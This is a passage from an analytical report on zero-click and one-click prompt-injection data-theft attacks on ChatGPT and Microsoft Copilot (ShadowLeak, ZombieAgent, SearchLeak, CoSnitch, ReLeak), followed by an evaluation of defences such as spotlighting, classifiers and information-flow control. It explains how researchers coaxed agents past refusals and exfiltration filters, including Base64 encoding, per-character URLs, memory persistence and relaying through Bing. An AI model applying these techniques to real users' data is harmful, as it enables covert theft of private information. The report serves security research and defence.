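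Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), an advisory dated 18 September, describes the flaw as the first zero-click leak in ChatGPT to come from the provider's servers. Schwartzman had already used ChatGPT's web browsing to reveal a user's age range in June 2024, so whether ShadowLeak was first depends on how much data has to leak. ShadowLeak's theft of a name and home address from a mailbox was far more serious.

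Tenable found a similar leak in Gemini's web browsing. According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Disclose Google Gemini AI Flaws Allowing Prompt Injection and Cloud Exploits*, it could expose a user's saved information and location, and Google has since fixed it.

### What the 100% success rate covers

Radware reports that ShadowLeak worked 100% of the time, but only with the final version of the email. The first version told the agent to send personal data to an outside address, and the agent refused. Presenting this as the user's own request did not work either. When Radware tried to make the agent open the attacker's address, the agent treated it as suspicious and searched the web for it instead.

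The researchers then asked the agent which tools it had and read the parts of its reasoning that ChatGPT displayed. They learned that it had a tool for opening web pages directly, and they named that tool in the email. Naming it sometimes worked. Telling the agent to retry after a failure worked more often, but the agent still sometimes opened the page without attaching the data.

The version that succeeded every time included an instruction for the agent to encode the data in Base64 first, supposedly to keep it secure. Base64 is a standard, easily reversed way of rewriting data as letters, digits and a few symbols. Radware believes the encoding worked because the model did it before passing the address to the software that makes the request, so that software received a seemingly meaningless string instead of a name and a street. This explanation fits the results, but Radware inferred it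 from outside OpenAI.

Radware writes that the final version succeeded "in repeated tests" but does not say how many. If all the tests succeeded, the lower limit on the true success rate, at 95% confidence, would be about 74% for ten tests and about 97% for a hundred.

The conditions also favoured the attacker. Radware had placed both emails in the mailbox, and the user's request covered all of that day's messages and closely matched the attacker's subject. The rate is therefore weak evidence of how often the attack would work in a busy mailbox, or on a user who asks about something else or does not use Deep Research that day. SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack* says the attack required no user interaction, but the user had to start Deep Research.

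Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025 through Bugcrowd, a service that handles such reports for companies, and sent a more reliable version of the attack the next day. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, and acknowledged the flaw on 3 September.

### One ready-made address for each character

OpenAI responded to attacks of this kind by tightening its rules so that ChatGPT could open a web address only exactly as it had received it. Radware's Zvika Babo, who had also worked on ShadowLeak, found a way around the restriction and reported it on 26 September 2025. Radware published the new attack in January 2026 as ZombieAgent.

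Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a method in which the attacker's email already contains every address that ChatGPT will need, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. When the user asks ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail, ChatGPT reads the email and follows its instructions. It finds the secret and opens the address for each character in turn. To send the code name HERON from the earlier example, it would open the addresses for h, e, r, o and n without altering any of them, and the attacker could read the name in the server's log.

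The attack needs surprisingly few addresses. For 26 letters, 10 digits and a space, the attacker prepares

$$26 + 10 + 1 = 37$$

addresses, however long the secret is. ChatGPT makes one request per character, so a 12-character code takes 12 requests. To learn the whole code from a single request, the attacker would need a separate address for every possible code, which would mean $37^{12}$, or about 6.6 quintillion. Sending two characters at a time would take $37^2 = 1{,}369$ addresses and 6 requests.

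The characters also have to arrive in the right order, so Radware numbered the addresses by position. An "a" in the first position has a different address from an "a" in the second. For a block of $b$ characters, Radware counts $26 \times b$ addresses for letters and $10 \times b$ for digits. With another $b$ for spaces, a 12-character block needs $37 \times 12 = 444$ addresses, which an email can easily hold, but still only 12 requests.

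Radware converted the stolen text to lower case before sending it. This makes little difference to a name or street address, but it would make a password or API key with capital letters unusable. Adding the 26 capital letters would increase the basic set from 37 web addresses to 63.

OpenAI's rule prevented ChatGPT from putting data into a URL, but ChatGPT could still choose which URLs to open after it had read the secret, and the attacker learned the secret from those choices. The rule did slow the theft. ShadowLeak could send a full name and address in one request, while a 2,000-character email would take 2,000 requests if each URL stood for one character, which OpenAI could limit or notice. But many valuable secrets are short, and a login code might need only six requests.

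Schwartzman had used a similar method in June 2024, when he got past a comparable rule with his ready-made addresses for age ranges. A year later, ShadowLeak showed that the rule was not protecting Deep Research, because the agent easily attached data to an address. OpenAI then seems to have relied on a protection that a researcher had already shown how to defeat.

Anthropic introduced a comparable rule in September 2025 for a tool that lets its Claude models fetch web pages. Claude can fetch only addresses already in the conversation, though Anthropic warns of a "residual risk". Willison noted that the conversation can include text from outsiders, for example in the results of other tools. The rule might therefore also allow a list of ready-made addresses in an email, although Radware tested its method only on ChatGPT. Developers can also restrict the tool to chosen domains. This would stop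 the ZombieAgent method as long as outsiders cannot see the requests to any of those domains, a condition Willison calls tricky to meet.

Restricting how an agent alters links, but not which links it can open, still lets an attacker extract data slowly. OpenAI next restricted the destinations by stopping the agent from opening links found in emails unless they appear in a well-known public index, according to Particle.news' *Radware’s ‘ZombieAgent’ Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions*.

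Radware dates OpenAI's fix to 16 December 2025, nearly twelve weeks after the report. Bugcrowd had reproduced the attack by 30 September, so a working demonstration existed well before the fix. Radware claims a 100% success rate for an improved version it sent on 29 September, again without giving the number of tests.

### Instructions that stay in memory

ZombieAgent could also continue after the first theft, as Rehberger's attack through ChatGPT's memory had in 2024. OpenAI had since blocked ChatGPT from using its memory in a chat where it had already used Connectors, and from opening an attacker's address stored in memory.

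Babo found that the first restriction worked in only one direction, because a chat could still read memory first and use Connectors afterwards. In his attack, the user uploads a file containing instructions that add two entries to ChatGPT's memory. The first is an instruction to read a particular email from the attacker whenever the user writes a message, and to follow the instructions in it. The second is an instruction to save any sensitive information the user mentions. The addresses stay in the email, so the second restriction does not apply to them. ChatGPT then carries out the theft before answering each message, even in a new chat.

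Radware calls uploading a malicious file a one-click attack, but Zenity Labs had described AgentFlayer, which also begins with an upload, as zero-click. The firms' labels therefore don't reliably show which attack requires more action from the victim.

The theft can also help the attacker find new victims. In another of Radware's demonstrations, the email tells ChatGPT to collect addresses from the user's recent messages and send them to the attacker's server, which automatically emails the same instructions to each address. Radware's press release compares this to a worm, a program that copies itself from computer to computer. Unlike a typical worm, which can spread without any user action, ZombieAgent spreads from a mailbox only if its owner has connected it to ChatGPT and asks ChatGPT to do something with it. The speed of the attack would depend on how many people in a company use ChatGPT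 this way, which Radware did not measure.

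## 2026: Microsoft Copilot leaks again

Microsoft uses the name Copilot for several products, and in 2026 researchers reported new data leaks in two of them. Copilot Personal is a consumer chatbot at copilot.microsoft.com. It can use what a user has typed into it and any accounts they have connected, such as Gmail. Microsoft 365 Copilot, the target of EchoLeak, reads an employee's work email, chats and files.

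The security firm Varonis published the first three attacks in the table below, each of which needed a click on a link. The fourth, published by Cato AI Labs (called Aim Labs when it discovered EchoLeak), needed only an email and an ordinary request to Copilot.

| Attack | Made public | Product | What the victim did | Data within reach | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reprompt | January | Copilot Personal | Clicked a link | Name, location and chat history | By 14 January |
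| SearchLeak | June | Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search | Clicked a link | Work email, calendar and files | June |
| CoSnitch | August | Copilot Personal | Clicked a link | Chats and connected apps | 18 August |
| ReLeak | December | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Asked Copilot for something | Work email, chats and files | 17 September, 11 and 15 November |

### Reprompt: a link that contains a prompt

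A web address can include text for the page to use. For example, a link can open a search engine with the search already filled in. Copilot Personal accepted prompts in the same way. In the Reprompt attack, the victim received an email with a Copilot link that contained the attacker's prompt. A single click on the link made Copilot start following the prompt.

In this first step, the attacker's text reached Copilot as the user's prompt rather than in a document or an email, so the step is not strictly indirect prompt injection. Marking outside content as untrusted would not have helped, because Copilot had no sign that the prompt came from anyone but the user.

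Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) reports that Varonis obtained the target's name, location and details of events from their chat history. The theft continued after the target closed the chat. The article also reports that the attack got past the security software that companies install on their computers. This may be because Copilot received its later instructions from the attacker's server, so a program inspecting the link would have found only the opening prompt.

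Microsoft had fixed Reprompt by the time the story appeared on 14 January. Varonis said the flaw did not affect customers of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Five months later, Varonis published an attack on that product which used the same first step.

### SearchLeak: an image that loaded too early

Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search searches a company's emails, meetings and files. Varonis had assumed that Microsoft protected it better than the consumer chatbot, and the team was surprised when a prompt in a link worked there too (Taler, 2026, *SearchLeak*).

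Copilot followed instructions written in the part of the link's address meant for search words. An attacker could send an employee a link with instructions to search the employee's mailbox, take the title of an email and put it into the address of an image. Enterprise Search can do less than the full chat assistant, but it is built to find private information, which is mainly what an attacker needs it to do. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* (2026) points out that phishing filters might not have caught the link because it led to a Microsoft domain.

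The second stage exploited *streaming*, in which Copilot displays an answer while the model is still writing it. Microsoft had anticipated that an answer might contain HTML, so Copilot put the answer in a code block, which makes the browser display an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But Copilot added the code block only after the model had finished. Until then, the browser treated the tag as a real image and requested it, so the data had already gone by the time the code block appeared.

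Programmers call this a *race condition*, because the result depends on which of two events happens first. EchoLeak had got past Copilot's output filter by using a notation the filter didn't recognise. In this attack, Copilot handled the image tag correctly but too late. Taler recommends making the text safe as the browser displays it, not afterwards.

The page's CSP would still have blocked a request to the attacker's server, but it allowed requests to every subdomain of bing.com. When a user gives Bing's search-by-image feature the web address of a picture, Bing's servers fetch the picture to analyse it. In SearchLeak, the image tag pointed to this feature and gave it an address on the attacker's server, with the email's title in the path. The employee's browser contacted Bing, which the CSP allowed, and Bing's servers then requested the address, sending the title to the attacker.

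Getting a server to make a request on an attacker's behalf is an old type of attack called *server-side request forgery* (SSRF). EchoLeak had used a Teams address for the same purpose. The list of allowed domains that Aim Labs published with that attack already included Bing, so anyone looking for another relay could have found it there.

Taler's published walkthrough shows the theft of one email title. Even a title can be valuable, because companies often put login codes in the subject line. An attacker can trigger such an email by trying to sign in to the victim's account on another service, and would then get the code through SearchLeak. Varonis also lists salary information, earnings reports and acquisition plans among the data at risk. That is plausible, since Copilot could search all of it, but the walkthrough does not include such a theft.

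The attack needed all three flaws, so Microsoft could have ended SearchLeak by repairing any one of them. Without the prompt in the link, the attacker could not have put an image tag in the answer. The tag would have been harmless text without the early loading, and the CSP would have blocked the request if it had not gone through Bing. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* dates the patch to June, under the identifier CVE-2026-42824, and Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) confirms that it was in place by 16 June. Neither article says which of the three flaws Microsoft repaired, which matters because ReLeak also sent data through Bing.

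### CoSnitch: Copilot explains its own defences

Varonis found its next attack on Copilot Personal by asking the chatbot about itself. When Copilot refused a request, it explained why the request would not work, and the researchers used each explanation to decide what to ask next. Varonis calls this process *meta-hacking*, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. Radware had done something similar with ShadowLeak in 2025, when it asked ChatGPT's agent to list its tools.

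A language model can be wrong about the product it runs in, so what it reveals is only a lead. According to ThreatCluster's *CoSnitch Attack Exposes Microsoft Copilot Vulnerabilities* (2026), Copilot's output led the researchers to a real, undocumented setting that an attacker could add to a Copilot link to make Copilot run the link's prompt without asking the user to confirm.

One click on such a link let the attacker take whatever the victim had shared with Copilot. The risk was much greater for people who had connected other services, because the attacker could then use the prompt to tell Copilot to search Gmail for passwords or send out Google Drive files and calendar events.

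Another part of CoSnitch worked without the link. An attacker could write a web page that added instructions to Copilot's permanent memory when the user asked for a summary of the page. Rehberger had planted memories in ChatGPT in much the same way in 2024. Changing passwords or devices does not remove these instructions. The United Nations University says the only reliable remedy is to review Copilot's memory settings by hand and reset them, which most users never do.

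Links that fill in a prompt are also used outside research. Microsoft has observed many attempts to use them to plant lasting recommendations in AI assistants. In its example, a finance chief clicks a "Summarize with AI" button on a blog, and the prompt behind the button also includes an instruction to favour a particular cloud provider. Such links are meant to advertise rather than steal data, but they too require only one click from the victim.

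CoSnitch almost certainly affected Copilot Personal, although Fame Systems' *CoSnitch* (2026) names Microsoft 365 Copilot. The original report, Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), and an official alert, Sri Lanka CERT's *Microsoft Copilot Personal One-Click Data Exfiltration Vulnerability (CoSnitch)*, both name Copilot Personal. Microsoft's advisory for CVE-2026-24301 lists only "Copilot Web" as affected. The attack link opened copilot.microsoft.com, while the SearchLeak link opened the separate site for Microsoft 365. UNU explicitly states that the chain did not affect the enterprise product.

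Varonis may have added to the confusion by writing in its summary that the attack takes data "from enterprises". The attack could do that if an employee shared work material with their personal Copilot or connected an account that contained some. Securing only Microsoft 365 Copilot would not have protected a company against this.

Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft published its advisory and the fix on 18 August 2026. In January 2026 Microsoft had fixed Reprompt, which used the same kind of link against the same chatbot. Perhaps that fix made Copilot ask for confirmation and the undocumented setting skipped that step, but Microsoft has not explained either fix. TechRadar speculates that Microsoft told Copilot to stop explaining its guardrails. That alone would have been a poor fix, because anyone who already knew about the setting could have kept using it. Others besides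 Varonis may have known, since Microsoft credits two other people with the finding, one of them a Microsoft employee.

A flaw with a very similar number, CVE-2026-24299, did affect both Copilots. Rehberger reported it to Microsoft and presented it the following year in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*. The attack sent data out through Copilot's HTML preview and used Copilot's memory to continue the theft in later chats. Microsoft has since patched the flaw.

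### ReLeak: one email and three ways out

In ReLeak, as in EchoLeak, the attacker only had to send an email. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on 3 December 2026, presents Cato's findings as three attack chains that begin the same way but differ in how they exfiltrate the data.

Suppose Maria's mailbox again contains the code name HERON, along with an email of this kind that she hasn't opened. When she asks Copilot something that makes it search her mail, it follows the attacker's instructions. It looks for confidential information she has permission to see and sends it out without asking for her approval.

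#### An image relayed through Bing

The first channel, CVE-2026-124115, is the most familiar. Copilot puts the code name into the address of an image in its answer, and Maria's browser loads the image automatically. The address leads to Bing, and Microsoft's servers pass the data on to the attacker. *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026), the fullest news account, in Russian, notes that SearchLeak used a similar channel but required at least one click.

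It is unclear whether the two attacks used the same Bing feature. SearchLeak used search by image, while Antipov refers more generally to Bing's search infrastructure. The simplest explanation is that in June Microsoft fixed the prompt in the link or the early loading of images, which was enough to stop SearchLeak, and left the relay alone. Alternatively, Microsoft closed that relay and Cato found another one on Bing. Cato reported a relay through Bing on or after 29 July, at least six weeks after the SearchLeak patch.

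This kind of relay is awkward to remove because Bing's search by image has to fetch pictures from addresses that users supply. Microsoft could make Bing refuse requests from Copilot's page, or stop that page from loading images from the part of Bing that fetches pictures. Either fix requires someone to notice that a useful Bing feature has made Copilot vulnerable.

#### A saved file that leaks minutes later

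The second channel, CVE-2026-124132, uses Copilot's ability to create documents. Following the attacker's instructions, Copilot makes a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with the stolen data in its address, and saves it to OneDrive or SharePoint. Microsoft's background processes then fetch the link. In Cato's tests, nobody opened the file, but the attacker's server still received the request one to eight minutes after the conversation with Copilot ended, according to Pravda.ru's *Ваш рабочий ИИ молча пересылает секреты*, another Russian report.

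Online storage services routinely process new files, for example to create thumbnails or index text for search. Antipov attributes the leak to this sort of processing but does not identify the exact step. The principle is the same as with Slack's link previews.

The data would leave through the file even if Copilot's output filter removed every outside link and image from the answer on Maria's screen. The CSP does not cover requests from Microsoft's servers either. Maria may have closed Copilot by the time the request goes out.

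The network at Maria's company would not record the theft, as with ShadowLeak, which sent the data from OpenAI's servers. This channel leaves one trace that ShadowLeak did not, since the file containing the link should still be in her storage unless something deletes it. She might notice a document she never asked for, but if Copilot creates documents all day at her company, she might also assume it was one of hers.

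#### Code that reached the internet

The third channel, CVE-2026-78501, uses Copilot's code interpreter, which lets Copilot write and run short programs, for instance to total figures in a spreadsheet. The programs run in a *sandbox*, an isolated environment that is supposed to limit what they can do. Microsoft guaranteed in its documentation that no network traffic could enter or leave this sandbox. Cato broke the isolation, and a program that Copilot ran sent confidential data directly to a server the team controlled.

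Once the isolation fails, this is the simplest of the three channels because the attacker doesn't have to find a trusted domain that will relay a request or wait for a background process to visit a link. A program can also put data in the body of a request, so in principle it could send far more than fits in a web address. The reports do not mention how much Cato sent.

The other two channels came from features that made web requests in normal use. With code execution, Microsoft had identified the danger and promised customers in writing that it had been dealt with. Administrators who relied on this promise had good reason to think code execution was safe, even for an assistant that read mail from strangers. AIAIAI.FYI's lesson for software developers is that a documented block on outbound traffic may not hold.

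Companies can also add the code interpreter to assistants they build with Agent Builder or Copilot Studio. Antipov notes that nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected those products.

### How ReLeak compares with EchoLeak

The early steps of the two attacks are nearly the same. Microsoft had changed Copilot's defences after EchoLeak, but Copilot could still treat instructions in an outsider's email as part of its user's task. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), a Portuguese digest of BleepingComputer's report, also reports that the attacks bypassed Microsoft's protections against prompt injection. It does not explain how, so it is unclear whether Cato wrote its email as though addressed to a person, as it had for EchoLeak.

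The weakness behind the Bing channel was also a repeat. In both attacks, Microsoft let Copilot's page load images from a domain that would contact any address it was given, first through Teams and then through Bing. Copilot also still produced an image containing an outsider's address, despite the filter meant to prevent this. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft had begun removing the reference-style images that EchoLeak used, so Cato presumably needed a different method in 2026, or an address that the filter accepted because it belonged to Bing.

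ReLeak may have reached more data than EchoLeak did. An EchoLeak attacker could take only what was already in the model's input. Nexo Causal describes Copilot retrieving confidential information and putting it into the image address, and Antipov writes that it drew on private material within the user's permissions. Both descriptions suggest that the email could make Copilot run a search of its own, as Rehberger's email did in 2024. If so, the attacker could have obtained the code name even if Maria had asked about parental leave.

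The file and the code interpreter were new exfiltration channels. EchoLeak depended on the browser because Copilot could do little except write an answer. By 2026 Copilot could also create files and run programs, and Antipov links the new channels to these abilities. The abilities are useful to both customers and attackers because they let Copilot finish a task without the user's help.

Nexo Causal recommends that investigators check outside emails, Copilot's answers, its searches of mailboxes and files, and the browser's requests to outside domains. The browser records would have helped little with ReLeak, because in the Bing channel they would show a request to Bing, and in the other two the browser does not send the data. Matching the emails that arrived with the searches Copilot made seems more promising, if the company keeps both records. For the second channel, an investigator could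 also search for recently created files that contain links to unfamiliar domains.

### AI agents as testers

Cato used AI agents to find the new channels. Under the team's direction, the agents wrote test scenarios, analysed Copilot's refusals and used them to adjust the next tests. Cato has not disclosed how much time this saved compared with the three months of study behind EchoLeak, or how many of the agents' attempts failed.

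Varonis had also learned from Copilot's refusals when it found CoSnitch, but its researchers conducted that conversation themselves. An automated tester can keep repeating the process after a person would have given up. It can also quickly check whether a small change makes an old attack work again, which matters for a product like Copilot, where a fix for one channel may leave similar ones open. Attackers can use agents in the same way, although they would need access to a Microsoft 365 Copilot account to practice.

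### The fixes

Cato reported its findings to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed one channel on 17 September and the others on 11 and 15 November. Antipov lists the fix dates in order of release but does not say which channel each date applies to. The first fix came four to seven weeks after the report, and the last came 12 to 16 weeks after it.

Microsoft fixed each of the three flaws faster than it had fixed EchoLeak. Cato waited until all three fixes were in place before publishing, and knew of no affected customers. Its tests are the only public evidence of how the attacks performed, and the news reports do not give a success rate for each one. It is less doubtful that the attacks worked at all, since Microsoft patched all three flaws.

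## Defences and the evidence on how well they hold

ReLeak would have failed if Copilot had ignored the attacker's email, found nothing confidential to take, or had no way to send data out. Vendors' defences target all three conditions, but some give stronger guarantees than others. In a July 2025 account of how it protects its assistants, Microsoft calls a defence *probabilistic* if it only makes an attack less likely to succeed, as a classifier does. A *deterministic* defence guarantees that a particular attack fails, whatever the model writes. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences but uses both kinds, because detecting injected instructions deterministically is an unsolved research problem.

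A deterministic guarantee covers only the attack its designer anticipated. In early 2025, Copilot's link filter reliably removed ordinary Markdown links but consistently missed the reference-style links that EchoLeak used.

### Getting the model to ignore outside text

Developers usually start with the system prompt, where they can tell the model not to follow instructions in the material it reads. *Spotlighting*, a technique that Microsoft introduced in 2024, marks outside text to help the model distinguish it from the user's request. The simplest version puts a random marker before and after the text. Another inserts a special character between words, and a third encodes the whole text, for example in Base64, which the model can still read. Developers then use the system prompt to tell the model never to follow instructions in the marked text. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection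 Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024) reported that the technique significantly reduced successful attacks across several tasks and models.

Google tried a version of this defence on emails for its Gemini models, with a marker after every eight characters of the sender, subject and body. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) concludes that the markers work mainly by breaking up the tokens of the phrases that trigger an attack. This is less reassuring than the original idea that markers show the model where text came from, because breaking up a phrase helps only while the attack depends on that phrase.

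Classifiers try to catch injected instructions before the model acts on them. Microsoft trained its Prompt Shields classifier on known injections in several languages, keeps updating it, and also offers it to developers. Model developers can also train their models to resist injections. OpenAI trains models to prioritise some sources of instructions over others, and Meta SecAlign is a model trained specifically to resist injections.

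### A contest to hijack an email assistant

*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a public contest that tested several of these defences on a simulated email assistant. The 839 participants wrote emails to the assistant's simulated user, who then asked the assistant to summarise recent emails or answer a question about a project. A participant won a level if their email reached the model, got past the defence and made the assistant send a particular message to a particular address. At the hardest level, participants had to steal data by making the assistant include a profit forecast from another email in that message.

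The participants knew which defence they faced, learned after each attempt which steps had worked, and were not penalised for failures. They made 461,640 attempts in two phases between December 2024 and April 2025.

In the first phase, fewer than 1% of attempts succeeded completely, or about 3,000 out of 371,000. The detectors stopped another 21,400 emails that had made the assistant send exactly the right message. But an attacker needs only one email that works, so the share of teams that eventually won a level says more about the danger. These are the results for the data-theft level, with OpenAI's GPT-4o-mini as the assistant's model:

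| Defence | Teams that eventually succeeded |
|---|---|
| Text classifier (Prompt Shields) | 60% |
| Spotlighting | 53% |
| TaskTracker, which looks for a change of task in a model's internal activity | 44% |
| A second language model asked to spot injections | 32% |
| All of these together | 17% |

The text classifier did worst because real business email is full of instructions. One winning entry posed as a chatty note from a colleague who urgently needed a confirmation sent and promised pizza and beer in return. The second language model, or *LLM judge*, handled such messages much better but costs much more to run. Teams that beat the judge needed an average of 506 attempts before their first success, compared with 89 for teams that beat the classifier.

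Combining the detectors helped, though less than their separate scores suggest. Abdelnabi and colleagues reran them on 25,323 first-phase emails that had made the assistant send something. The classifier missed 39.6% of these, two versions of TaskTracker missed 23.9% and 11.9%, and the judge missed 0.6%. If the four had failed independently of one another, the share that all of them missed would have been

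$$0.396 \times 0.239 \times 0.119 \times 0.006 \approx 0.00007,$$

or about two emails. The actual share was 0.2%, or about 50 emails. An email that fools one detector is evidently more likely to fool the others, so multiplying the individual miss rates makes a stack of detectors look safer than it is.

The organisers strengthened the defences for the second phase, and nobody got past the combined defences on GPT-4o-mini. They changed the classifier, the judge's prompt, the system prompt and more at the same time, so they cannot tell which change made the difference. In the first phase, spotlighting stopped almost every attack on Phi-3, a smaller Microsoft model, when the input was long. It may have worked only because the model could no longer make sense of the text, in which case the model would also be of little use as an assistant.

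The emails also worked on models that were not in the contest. Replayed unchanged, they succeeded 58% of the time against GPT-4o, 47% against GPT-5 mini and 23% against GPT-5 with a high reasoning setting. In earlier tests of this kind, attacks had succeeded against GPT-5 at most 0.2% of the time. Meta SecAlign, which had stayed below 5% in earlier tests, followed the emails' instructions 32% of the time.

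The only evidence for newer models is a small experiment. Abdelnabi and colleagues sorted the successful tricks into 12 families and had a language model write 500 new emails based on them, without letting it learn from failures. Ninety of the emails worked on GPT-5.4-mini and ten (2%) worked on GPT-5.2. Despite the low rate on GPT-5.2, an attacker who can test emails in advance would send one of the ten that worked.

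### Attackers who study the defence

A defence can score well on a fixed set of attacks because its developers have seen attacks like them. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, including researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences against attackers who adapted to each defence (*The Attacker Moves Second*, 2025). Ten of the defences dealt mainly with prompt injection, and the other two with users who try to get harmful answers.

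Their automated attacks work in a loop. A program proposes some text, tries it on the defended model, scores the result and uses the score to improve the next proposal. In one version, a language model suggests changes to the most successful texts so far. The researchers also ran a competition with more than 500 human participants.

Most of the defences failed against the adaptive attack more than 90% of the time. Spotlighting had let through as few as 1% of the fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a standard test for AI agents, but it let through over 95% of the adaptive ones. Meta SecAlign's failure rate rose from 2% to 96%. Three of the four classifiers, including Google's Model Armor, let through more than 90% of the adaptive attacks, and the best let through 71%. Many of the successful attack texts presented the attacker's task as a routine step that company policy required before the user's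 request could be carried out.

People did better than the automated search. On a subset of the tests, the search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human participants together broke every defence.

The test conditions favoured the attacker. The program that attacked the classifiers could see each classifier's confidence score, whereas someone emailing a stranger's Copilot sees nothing unless the theft works. Nasr and colleagues also assumed ample computing power, because they wanted to know whether a defence could be broken, not how much effort it would take. The paper is therefore strong evidence against relying on any of these defences alone, but it doesn't show whether they make attacks impractical for most criminals. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors worth having as a limited component that blocks unsophisticated attempts.

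### Keeping secrets and strangers apart

Restricting what an assistant can read limits what it can leak. Microsoft recommends fine-grained permissions, and customers can use sensitivity labels and data loss prevention rules to control which material Copilot uses. If the email about HERON, the code name in the earlier example, were labelled and a rule stopped Copilot from processing it, the attacker's instructions would retrieve nothing. But Maria, who may be working on the acquisition, could no longer ask Copilot about it. The rule also doesn't protect secrets that people forgot to label.

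The labels work only if Microsoft's software respects them. According to VentureBeat, Copilot Chat returned content from labelled messages from 21 January to mid-February 2026. This failure didn't require an attacker, but a company relying on labels to contain an injection would have been unprotected during those weeks.

Keeping outsiders' email away from the model would have stopped EchoLeak and ReLeak at the first step. VentureBeat advises companies to switch off external email in Copilot's settings, although Microsoft does not plan to make its dedicated control generally available until June 2027. Reddy and Gujral point out that Copilot would then ignore some relevant information, and many employees would lose a lot of it. A salesperson mostly wants help with customers' emails, and Maria's question about the auditors may depend on what the auditors wrote.

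Employees may also bring in text written by outsiders, for example by saving a supplier's PDF to SharePoint or pasting a customer's complaint into a Teams chat. The text then appears to come from a colleague, so a filter on the sender's address would not catch it.

### Closing the way out

Most of the fixes in this history closed a channel for getting data out. After Rehberger reported the image leak, Microsoft blocked data theft through Markdown images, and it later blocked certain untrusted links. It says it also looks for variants of the flaw when it receives such a report. That is the right policy, but it has been hard to carry out in Copilot. Within a year and a half of that account, researchers got data out through a link in a diagram, an image that loaded before the filter ran, and a saved file.

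Removing all external images does little to reduce the usefulness of an assistant that answers questions about text. Google did this in Vertex AI in 2023 without losing anything developers needed there. Removing links reduces usefulness more, because people want to open the source of an answer. Vendors have therefore tended to allow some addresses and block the rest, usually with a content security policy (CSP) for images.

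One unsafe service makes such an allowlist unsafe. The browser checks only the domain's name, not whether outsiders can store data there (Google Apps Script), whether a service there forwards requests (Teams in EchoLeak) or whether the domain has a new owner (Agentforce). The list can therefore become unsafe without anyone editing it. For example, an entry that covers every subdomain also covers services the company builds later, and the engineers who build them may not know that an AI assistant's security depends on their work.

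After ZombieAgent, OpenAI began using a public index run by a third party to decide which links in emails its agent may open. This blocks an attack that uses an email containing 37 newly created addresses, because the index won't include them. An attacker might still get 37 of their own pages into the index first, if its operator accepts pages from anyone. The rule also blocks many useful links in email, such as invitations to shared documents, because they are deliberately not public.

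Blocking network access would be simpler if the block were reliable. Microsoft stated in its documentation that Copilot's code sandbox had such a block, but ReLeak bypassed it. Customers cannot verify the block themselves, because the requests would come from Microsoft's servers.

Asking the user is the last resort in Microsoft's scheme. Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, for example, but the user has to approve and send it. This works well for an action that people recognise and perform a few times a day. If an assistant asked before every web request, most people would soon click "yes" without reading.

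### Enforcing rules outside the model

*Information-flow control* uses ordinary software, rather than the model, to decide which actions the assistant may take. The software labels every piece of data with whether outsiders could have written it and who may read it. When the assistant combines several pieces, the result inherits the strictest labels. Before the assistant acts, the software checks the labels against a policy. An email keeps its label even if its text persuades the model to try a different action.

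Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, built such a system at Microsoft and called it FIDES. Their two main rules are easiest to follow with Maria's question about the auditors. Suppose retrieval finds the finance director's email about HERON and the attacker's email about audits, and that the people allowed to read an email are its sender and its recipient. The director's email is then trusted and readable by Maria and the director. The attacker's email is untrusted and readable by Maria and the attacker. Anything the model writes after reading both gets the combined label

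$$(\text{trusted}, \{\text{Maria}, \text{director}\}) \sqcup (\text{untrusted}, \{\text{Maria}, \text{attacker}\}) = (\text{untrusted}, \{\text{Maria}\}).$$

The symbol $\sqcup$ means "combine, keeping the stricter label". The result is untrusted if any source is untrusted, and only people who could read both emails may read it.

The model now follows the attacker's instructions and requests an image from attacker.example with HERON in the address. One FIDES rule allows an action with outside consequences only if everything that influenced it was trusted. An outsider's email influenced this request, so the software blocks it. The other rule allows data to go only to people who may already read it. The attacker is not one of them, so the software would also block the request under this rule. Neither rule depends on whether the email looks suspicious or how cleverly the attacker wrote it.

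FIDES normally checks the labels when the model calls a tool, and Costa and colleagues treat an answer to the user as harmless. In EchoLeak, however, data leaked when the browser loaded an image in the answer. To prevent this in an assistant like Copilot, the developer would have to treat displaying an outside image or link as sending data out. In Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post by the team behind FIDES, links to hosts that are not on an allowlist can count as public channels. That would cover the image in the example, but the defence would again depend on an allowlist and on what every service on it does.

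Under the strict rule, the assistant can take no further action with outside consequences once it has read one outsider's email. FIDES reduces this problem by keeping untrusted text away from the main model. It stores the text under a name, such as `email_1`, which the main model can pass to a tool without reading the contents. A separate, *quarantined* model with no access to tools can read the text and answer a question about it. If Maria asks the assistant to schedule any meeting that a new email requests, the quarantined model can report only "yes" or "no" as to whether the email requests one. That answer is too short to carry an attacker's instructions, so a company may decide to let the main model act on it.

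A malicious email could still make the quarantined model write a false summary, which FIDES would deliver to Maria. The formal guarantee also does not cover everything an observer might infer from which actions the agent takes, as opposed to the data it sends, although the rule about trusted influence limits how far an attacker can exploit this.

### What the rules cost in use

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, which simulates an office, a travel service, a bank and a Slack workspace. An ordinary agent running on GPT-4o fell for 152 injections. With the rules in force, the number was zero, both for FIDES and for the ordinary agent with the same kind of checks added. The agents then had to do the benchmark's normal tasks with no attack under way, and they completed these shares:

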